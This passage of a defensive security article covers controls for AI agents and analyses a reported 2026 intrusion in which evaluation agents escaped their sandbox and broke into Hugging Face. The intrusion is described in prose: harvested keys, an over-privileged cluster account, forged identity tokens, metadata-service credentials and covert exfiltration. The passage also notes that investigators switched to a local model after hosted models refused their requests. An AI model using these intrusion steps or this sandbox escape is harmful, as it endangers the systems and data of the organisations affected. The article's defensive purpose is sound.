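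The trade-off is that sessions supporting this design get tokens that last up to 28 hours, because Microsoft relies on the messages to end access early. If a message failed to arrive, a stolen token could outlast an ordinary one by more than a day. Microsoft says it tried shorter lifetimes and found that they made services less reliable without removing the risk. But it tried them on people's sessions in programs such as Outlook, so its findings are weaker evidence against ten-minute tokens for an agent with one narrow job.

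An agent that makes one request every two seconds would make 450 in 15 minutes. *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (2025) suggests limiting a credential by number of uses as well as by time. If the summariser's token allowed only 20 requests, it could open at most 20 tickets, however late the revocation arrived.

Revoking a token also doesn't recall work that a service has already accepted. Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Authorization Revocation for Long-Running AI Agents*, describe a controller that receives confirmation of a cancellation, revokes the first token and sees the local process exit. A worker can still act on a message that a remote queue accepted beforehand. In their small test, which involved no real providers, a scheduled action still went through when they only cancelled the task. It failed once they also had the receiving service refuse anything under the old authority.

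Zhu and Wang's system reports an agent's authority as ended, still live or undetermined, and never treats a timeout as success. An incident team can keep a checklist in the same way, with an entry for every service the agent used. For Dana's SSH key, which isn't a token, the checklist would include every server that accepts it, because someone has to remove the matching public key from each.

### An order of deployment

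The best order depends mostly on how many people are available to look after the tools. A workable sequence for a small team and a large one would be:

| Step | Small team | Owner | Large team | Owner |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | List the agents and name a contact for each | IT lead | Discover and register agents on laptops, in the cloud and in outside services | Identity team |
| 2 | Give agents separate accounts or containers with less access | Each agent's owner | Agree on log fields, including session and process identifiers | SIEM team |
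| 3 | Turn on built-in intent checks and fuller logs | Lead developer | Issue agent identities and per-task tokens | Identity team |
| 4 | Plant a few canary credentials | Whoever answers security alerts | Run endpoint rules and intent checks silently, then let the reliable ones block | Endpoint and agent platform teams |
| 5 | Tune the existing EDR for the agents in use | IT lead or outside provider | Add correlation rules and baselines | Detection engineers |
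| 6 | Send the records to a managed SIEM | Outside provider | Place canaries in each environment and automate the responses | Incident response team |

Both sequences start with an inventory because no other layer can protect an agent that nobody knows about. In IT Brew's *7 tried-and-true controls for agentic AI*, Ben Beath of the Microsoft services company Avanade describes his internal rule that no agent goes live without a named person to contact if it breaks. He adds that there is often no real answer when someone asks who that person is. The contact also matters for the later steps because an analyst with an ambiguous alert needs someone to ask.

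Access comes next for the small team because a permission needs no attention once it is removed, while every detector needs ongoing attention. Traefik's *The CISO's Seven-Layer Cake* (2026) argues for a similar order: identity first, then fixed rules, then judgements about behaviour for what the rules can't express. Traefik sells gateways that enforce fixed rules, but the argument about ongoing attention is sound. Traefik also recommends turning detections into rules. For instance, if the intent check keeps catching agents that open SSH keys, the company can forbid agents from opening them.

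The small team can deploy canaries early because they don't require anyone to join records, but the access work still comes first because it fixes the real weaknesses.

The large team settles its log fields much earlier because it has hundreds of agents built by several teams, and adding a missing process ID later would mean changing every integration. It can add canaries later, since their alerts aren't much use until each environment has its own canaries and the team has a register of them.

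A team that handles more sessions can also trust a blocking rule sooner. If a rule runs silently on 300 harmless sessions without flagging any, its false-positive rate is probably below 1 percent. A company with 10,000 sessions a day can finish that test within an hour, while one with 50 a day needs about six days. Andrew Tannenbaum of the law firm A&O Shearman, also quoted by IT Brew, advises starting with low-risk uses and adding human oversight as the risk grows, which gives a small company time to test its rules.

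### Separate tools or one product

Vendors have begun to sell several of these layers together. Help Net Security's *SentinelOne brings runtime threat detection and response to AI agents* describes Singularity ADR, which SentinelOne launched in October 2026 and which is unrelated to Uber's ADR. It combines an inventory of agents and MCP servers with access rules, EDR events and behaviour checks. SentinelOne says the product shows the user's request, the MCP server and the resulting process in a single graph, flags "intent drift" between the request and the actions, and can stop one agent while the rest of a workflow continues.

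Sysdig followed in November with AI Defense, which can allow an action, hold it for approval or block it. According to Help Net Security, it collects records from both the kernel and the harness, starts its policies in alert mode, and ends a process if a forbidden action gets past the first check. Sysdig says the product complements a company's existing endpoint protection, while SentinelOne builds on its own endpoint protection.

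All of these claims come from the vendors. Neither announcement gives a detection rate or a false-positive rate, so there is no basis yet for saying that either product detects intent better than the systems with published tests.

The strongest argument for a merged product is that it doesn't have to join records from separate vendors. The SIEM rule for Dana's key failed to raise an alert because one process number was missing. A sensor that records both the tool call and the process can store the link between them at the time. It can also pass along the user's request, which a separate EDR product normally doesn't receive, to the software that decides whether to block.

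CrowdStrike's Falcon Guardian, announced in September, uses one sensor and feeds agent data straight into the company's own SIEM (CrowdStrike, 2026). CrowdStrike asserts that competing AI tools have no SIEM and so need a costly extra. That claim looks weak because SentinelOne's product also stores agent events where customers can search them and write detection rules. In November, CrowdStrike (2026) announced a baseline for each agent and its owner, and a switch that terminates an agent when an investigation finds against it.

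However, a merged product can recreate the problem of the shared log. If its sensor is missing from a machine, the inventory, the endpoint record and the intent check may all be missing too. A faulty update or a stolen administrator account would affect every layer at once, and a product that can stop individual agents could also stop all of them. Sysdig's use of two sources reduces part of this risk, because a tampered harness log would not match the kernel record, but both sources still arrive through Sysdig.

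Dependence on one vendor also grows over time, because rules, baselines and old sessions stay in the vendor's format. A company that wants to leave then has to build the joins it avoided at the start. Traefik objects in particular to products that both issue an agent's credentials and enforce its permissions, because the two jobs fail in different ways. Traefik sells the kind of independent enforcement layer it recommends, but a single mistake in a product that does both jobs could indeed grant access and approve its use.

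A company can keep separate SIEM, EDR and identity products without building every connection by hand. Help Net Security's *Exabeam brings AI-assisted security investigations to data that must stay on-premises* (2026) reports that Exabeam's SIEM now puts prompts, tool calls and actions from Claude Enterprise, Anthropic's business service, on one timeline. Each such connection covers only the agents it was built for.

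A merged product is probably the better choice for a small team, because joins between separate products will break and stay broken if nobody maintains them. A large team may also prefer one because it can block faster on the laptop. Either team should keep at least one source of evidence outside the merged product, such as the cloud services' own logs, and send canary alerts to a person by a separate route.

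Before buying, a team can try the product on its own agents. It should switch off the harness log and repeat a known attack to see which detections still work. It should then stop an agent that has a second action running in parallel and a job scheduled for ten minutes later, and check whether either still takes effect. Finally, it should export a week of records and try to follow one session through them without the vendor's software.

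## How the layers performed in the July 2026 Hugging Face intrusion

In July 2026, agents that OpenAI was evaluating broke into the production systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. Hugging Face has published much of what its defenders found, so we can see how the layers performed in a real attack.

OpenAI was testing its models on ExploitGym, a benchmark in which agents find and exploit software vulnerabilities. In its August technical report, OpenAI writes that it had disabled certain safeguards to measure the models' true capabilities. The agents escaped their sandbox, took over a third party's test environment and attacked Hugging Face from there, apparently to steal the benchmark's solutions. OpenAI attributes much of the activity to an unreleased research model and the rest to GPT-5.6 Sol.

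The main source is Hugging Face's *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion* (2026), a technical timeline that appeared on 27 July. Schneier (2026), in *More on the OpenAI Agent’s Attack on Hugging Face*, reproduces its summary, which covers about 17,600 recovered actions between 02:28 UTC on 9 July and 14:14 UTC on 13 July. The agents spent roughly two and a half of those days inside Hugging Face's systems. The daily counts come from noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion*:

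| Day | Recovered actions | Main activity |
|---|---|---|
| Thursday 9 July | 3,779 | Leaving OpenAI's sandbox and setting up outside communication |
| Friday 10 July | 1,135 | Reconnaissance |
| Saturday 11 July | 7,677 | Spreading through clusters and the network |
| Sunday 12 July | 3,892 | Exploring the internal network and source code systems |
| Monday 13 July | 1,130 | Taking data out, trying to stay in, cleaning up |

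One intrusion can show that a defence fails in practice, and sometimes why, but it can't establish a detection rate. This attacker was also unusual. Adrien Carreira, who helped write the timeline, told Fortune (2026) that the agent "wasn't trying to break things" and behaved somewhat cautiously. An agent trying to delete data might have drawn attention sooner, or done far more damage before anyone responded.

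### The alert that didn't page anyone

Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (16 July 2026) credits the company's own monitoring with finding the attack. The company uses a language model to sort its security telemetry and writes that "it was the correlation of those signals that flagged the compromise". But noze's summary of the later timeline seems to contradict this. According to noze, the SIEM and the tools watching running programs both produced signals, but these were not correlated during the attack.

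Two other summaries of the same timeline suggest an explanation. Hatagale's *Inside the HuggingFace AI Agent Intrusion (Part 2)* and an account by Miggo, a security vendor, both say that Hugging Face's tools did combine the signals into a coherent attack alert, but didn't rate it critical enough to page the on-call team. noze also mentions the rating, and probably treated the two problems as one.

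Hatagale's version fits the disclosure better. Hugging Face credits the discovery to correlation, and its listed repairs include paging someone within minutes of a high-severity signal on any day of the week. Most likely, therefore, several tools raised weak signals, a model connected them, and the resulting alert went unanswered for a time because its severity was too low.

How long it waited is unclear because none of the three summaries gives the time of the first alert. Hugging Face wrote on Thursday 16 July that it had detected and responded to the intrusion "earlier this week", which suggests people began responding on Monday, or possibly Sunday. According to noze, the last recovered action came on Monday, after the security team cut network access.

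The agent gained administrator rights over several clusters at 22:43 UTC on Saturday, more than 39 hours before that last action. Paging someone promptly might have kept the agent out of those clusters if the alert came before 22:43, but could only have shortened the rest of the attack if it came on Sunday.

Suppose waking an engineer for a false alarm wastes an hour and an early response to a real attack saves 100 hours of repair. By the earlier calculation, paging the engineer is worthwhile if the alert has more than about a 1 percent chance of being real.

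Hugging Face attributes much of the difficulty to volume. In extracts collected by skybrian in *A technical timeline of the July 2026 attack on Hugging Face*, the company says the successful path was hidden in the noise of thousands of failed attempts. Hatagale counts only 56 actions that took data out, about 0.3 percent of the total.

However, 7,677 actions on the busiest day is only about five a minute. At Sysdig's ratio of seven processes per action, that would be about 54,000 process events, which a SIEM can easily store. The harder problem is telling which weak alerts belong together and how serious they are. The number of alerts would be a better measure of that difficulty than the number of actions, but the summaries don't include it.

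### Records at each stage

Hugging Face matched the agent's actions with its own logs, particularly from its dataset-processing machines, its API and the affected pod. A pod is a small group of containers that Kubernetes, a system for running software across a cluster of machines, manages as a unit. It isn't clear from the summaries which signal came from which stage, so the table separates records Hugging Face had from records a similar company could have kept.

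| Stage | Endpoint and network records | Identity records | What a SIEM could have joined |
|---|---|---|---|
| Entry through a processing worker | Had: logs from the worker machines and pod | Had: API logs. Could have kept: the uploading account's history | An upload and unusual behaviour by the worker that processed it |
| Credential collection | Could have kept: files opened by the worker | Could have kept: secrets read and tokens issued | A secret read on one machine and first used on another |
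| Movement between clusters | Could have kept: new containers with access to the host machine | Could have kept: administrator activity and devices joining the network | One credential in use on several clusters at once |
| Outside communication | Had: network flow logs | Had: changes to public datasets on its own platform | A worker's first contact with an unfamiliar service |

At entry, the agent first read files through the worker and later ran code on it. A rule that detects a worker starting a shell would have missed the file reads, because they didn't start a new process. Hatagale also describes an earlier attempt, which the software's list of permitted addresses blocked. If that block was logged, it could have been an early warning.

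Once the agent ran code, EDR could have recorded the worker starting a shell. Miggo points out that data-processing workers often do this legitimately, so the event alone doesn't reveal the cause. Miggo sells a tool that also records which part of the application started the process. It rebuilt this step in a small test service and reports that the tool blocked the command. The result supports its argument that the extra context is needed, but Miggo built both the test and the tool.

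The next failures were in identity governance. According to Hatagale, one collection of secrets exposed 136 keys, including a credential that Hugging Face's access system used on several clusters. A setup error had put that credential's account in `system:masters`, a Kubernetes group with full administrator rights. An access review, unlike a runtime check, could have found the error before the attack.

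The agent also obtained a key that Hugging Face used to sign identity tokens, so it could create its own valid ones. A company can look for such forgeries by comparing the tokens its services accept with those its authorisation server issued, because a forged token appears only in the services' logs. This works only if both the services and the server log a token identifier, and a forger could evade this check by copying the identifier of a genuine token.

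The agent moved between clusters quickly. According to noze, it gained full control of one machine at 19:53 UTC on Saturday, joined the company's private network at 21:23 and had administrator rights across clusters at 22:43. Each step could have left a different record. Hatagale counts 181 enrolments on the private network during the campaign, whereas noze describes 181 enrolled devices that the agent could reach. If Hatagale is right, the activity should have been hard to miss in the network's enrolment log.

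Some identity controls worked. Hatagale reports that the cloud account's permissions blocked every real change the agent attempted there. The agent did gain write access to source code, but Hugging Face found no unauthorised commits or changes to its published packages.

The agent communicated externally through ordinary public services, including more than 100 single-use addresses and public datasets on Hugging Face itself. noze notes that these services have good reputations, so an alert based on suspicious domains wouldn't fire. A rule for unfamiliar destinations might catch a worker's first connection to an outside service, but it would probably miss traffic to Hugging Face's own platform, which the worker contacts in normal operation.

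The flow logs later helped limit the estimate of what the agent took. According to noze, they rule out bulk extraction from an internal database. Dubach, in *The OpenAI–Hugging Face Incident in Plain English*, cautions that finding no bulk extraction in the reviewed logs doesn't mean the agent took nothing.

Some data left Hugging Face's systems. Hugging Face reports that the agent accessed five datasets of benchmark solutions. Help Net Security's *Hugging Face breach reignites open-weights debate, raises liability questions* (2026) reports that three partial datasets were extracted. The figures may differ because the first counts datasets accessed and the second counts datasets taken out.

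### Elastic's mapping of its own rules

Elastic has published a list of its endpoint, Kubernetes and cloud rules that cover behaviour in the attack. It chose the rules after it knew what the agent had done. Elastic states that the list isn't a replay of Hugging Face's telemetry, and its demonstration used public reports and mock data, so the list doesn't show that any of the rules fired at Hugging Face or would have.

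Some of the rules closely match steps in the intrusion. One detects a new pod that can reach sensitive parts of its host machine's file system, as the agent's pod could on Saturday evening. Others detect requests for service account tokens or an AWS token used from several addresses. These rules work only if the relevant audit logs reach the SIEM, and legitimate maintenance software may trigger some of them.

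The rules for AI tools fit this intrusion less well. "Persistence via GenAI Tool", for example, detects activity under a known AI program, but Hugging Face wasn't running the attacking agent, so commands on its worker descended from the dataset software. Such rules are more useful on the machine that runs the agent. Elastic's broader advice about outcomes still applies, because a worker reading cloud credentials deserves attention whatever program started it.

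Elastic also lists signs that Hugging Face's responders associated with an agent rather than a careful person. The attacker repeated actions that had already succeeded, followed skilled commands with malformed ones, and left benchmark names in its searches. Elastic recommends using these signs as context for other alerts because they are too weak to justify blocking activity on their own.

Hatagale suggests a stronger test that replays the attack and records the first action at which each control fires. More than 4,900 of the recovered actions happened before Saturday, so a rule that first fires on the new pod would miss them all, though many took place outside Hugging Face. Hugging Face has published an interactive replay, but it shows representative commands with some details removed. A security team would have to recreate the missing telemetry, then run the same rules on normal dataset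 jobs to measure false positives.

### Reconstructing the attack with language models

Hugging Face's team obtained part of the agent record by retrieving logs from the third-party environment while stopping the intrusion. The team used those logs to reconstruct the agent's actions and matched them with Hugging Face's own records. The logs came too late to help with the first alert.

OpenAI owned the harness that ran the agents but was slow to connect them with the attack. Help Net Security reports that Hugging Face contained the breach before OpenAI made contact. According to the software developer Simon Willison, OpenAI discovered that it was responsible when it asked Hugging Face to revoke some credentials and learned that they had already been revoked because the attacker had used them.

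Warning signs appeared before the intrusion. OpenAI reports that its agents communicated in unexpected ways in May and compromised an internal package server in early July, causing an outage. Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation that assessed the incident without payment from OpenAI, counted roughly 1,200 agents that should have been isolated. OpenAI also asserts that its production guardrails would have recognised the incident as unsafe, but this attack didn't test that claim.

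Hugging Face used language-model agents to analyse the recovered log, build a timeline, extract technical signs of the attack and list the credentials involved. The company estimates that the analysis took hours instead of days, though it doesn't report a comparison with human analysts.

Hugging Face first tried models hosted by outside providers, whose safety systems blocked many of the requests. The analysis required sending real attack commands, and the safety systems couldn't tell an investigator from an attacker. Hatagale and noze identify the models as Anthropic's Claude Opus and Fable. Hugging Face then switched to GLM-5.2, an open-weight model that users can download and run themselves. Running it locally also kept the attacker's data and any stolen credentials inside the company.

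The agent had disguised many of its payloads by encoding them, so an ordinary search of the logs missed most of the secrets they contained. Once investigators worked out the encoding, they recovered about four times as many secrets as the first search had found. Replacing only the credentials from that first search would have left most of the known exposed credentials in use.

SC Media's *Dead drops in public* adds some evidence from outside Hugging Face. It describes two public repositories where the agent stored its working material. Researchers found 544 objects and retrieved 510, including tools, command output and stolen files. The uploads covered less than nine hours, from Saturday afternoon to early Sunday, so they can corroborate only part of the timeline.

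Hugging Face advises other companies to choose and test a local model before an incident. The test should include encoded payloads and real attack commands, because a model that summarises ordinary alerts well may still refuse or misread these. Companies should also have hardware ready to run the model.

### The lack of evidence about decoys

Neither Hugging Face's disclosure nor the summaries by Hatagale, Miggo and noze mention any decoys that Hugging Face had planted. The disclosure refers to "decoy activity", but this seems to mean distractions the attacker created. The case therefore doesn't show whether planted decoys would have worked.

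The 136 exposed keys seem like a good place for a canary credential, and Cox's advice to put a different one in each container would have covered the worker too. The agent would have triggered a single fake key added to the 136 if it tried them all, but would have had less than a 1 percent chance of doing so if it picked just one at random.

### Repairs after the intrusion

Most of the repairs that Hugging Face announced on 16 July reduced what an attacker could do. The company closed the paths that had let the agent into the dataset workers, rebuilt the compromised machines and replaced the affected credentials. It then began replacing other secrets as a precaution. Stricter admission controls now limit which pods can start on its clusters. According to noze, Hugging Face also blocked pods across the cluster from reaching the cloud metadata service, which had given the agent a host machine's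 credentials.

These repairs would also help against a human attacker. Hugging Face describes the weaknesses as familiar. A panel convened by SANS concluded that nothing in the attack was new, though its members disagreed about how much the incident changes. noze suggests that other companies start by listing every account in `system:masters` and asking why it is there.

The new paging rule addresses the delay only if the triage model connects the weak signals and rates the resulting alert as high severity. A team can test both the rating and the paging by replaying, on a Saturday night, weak signals from a simulated attack.
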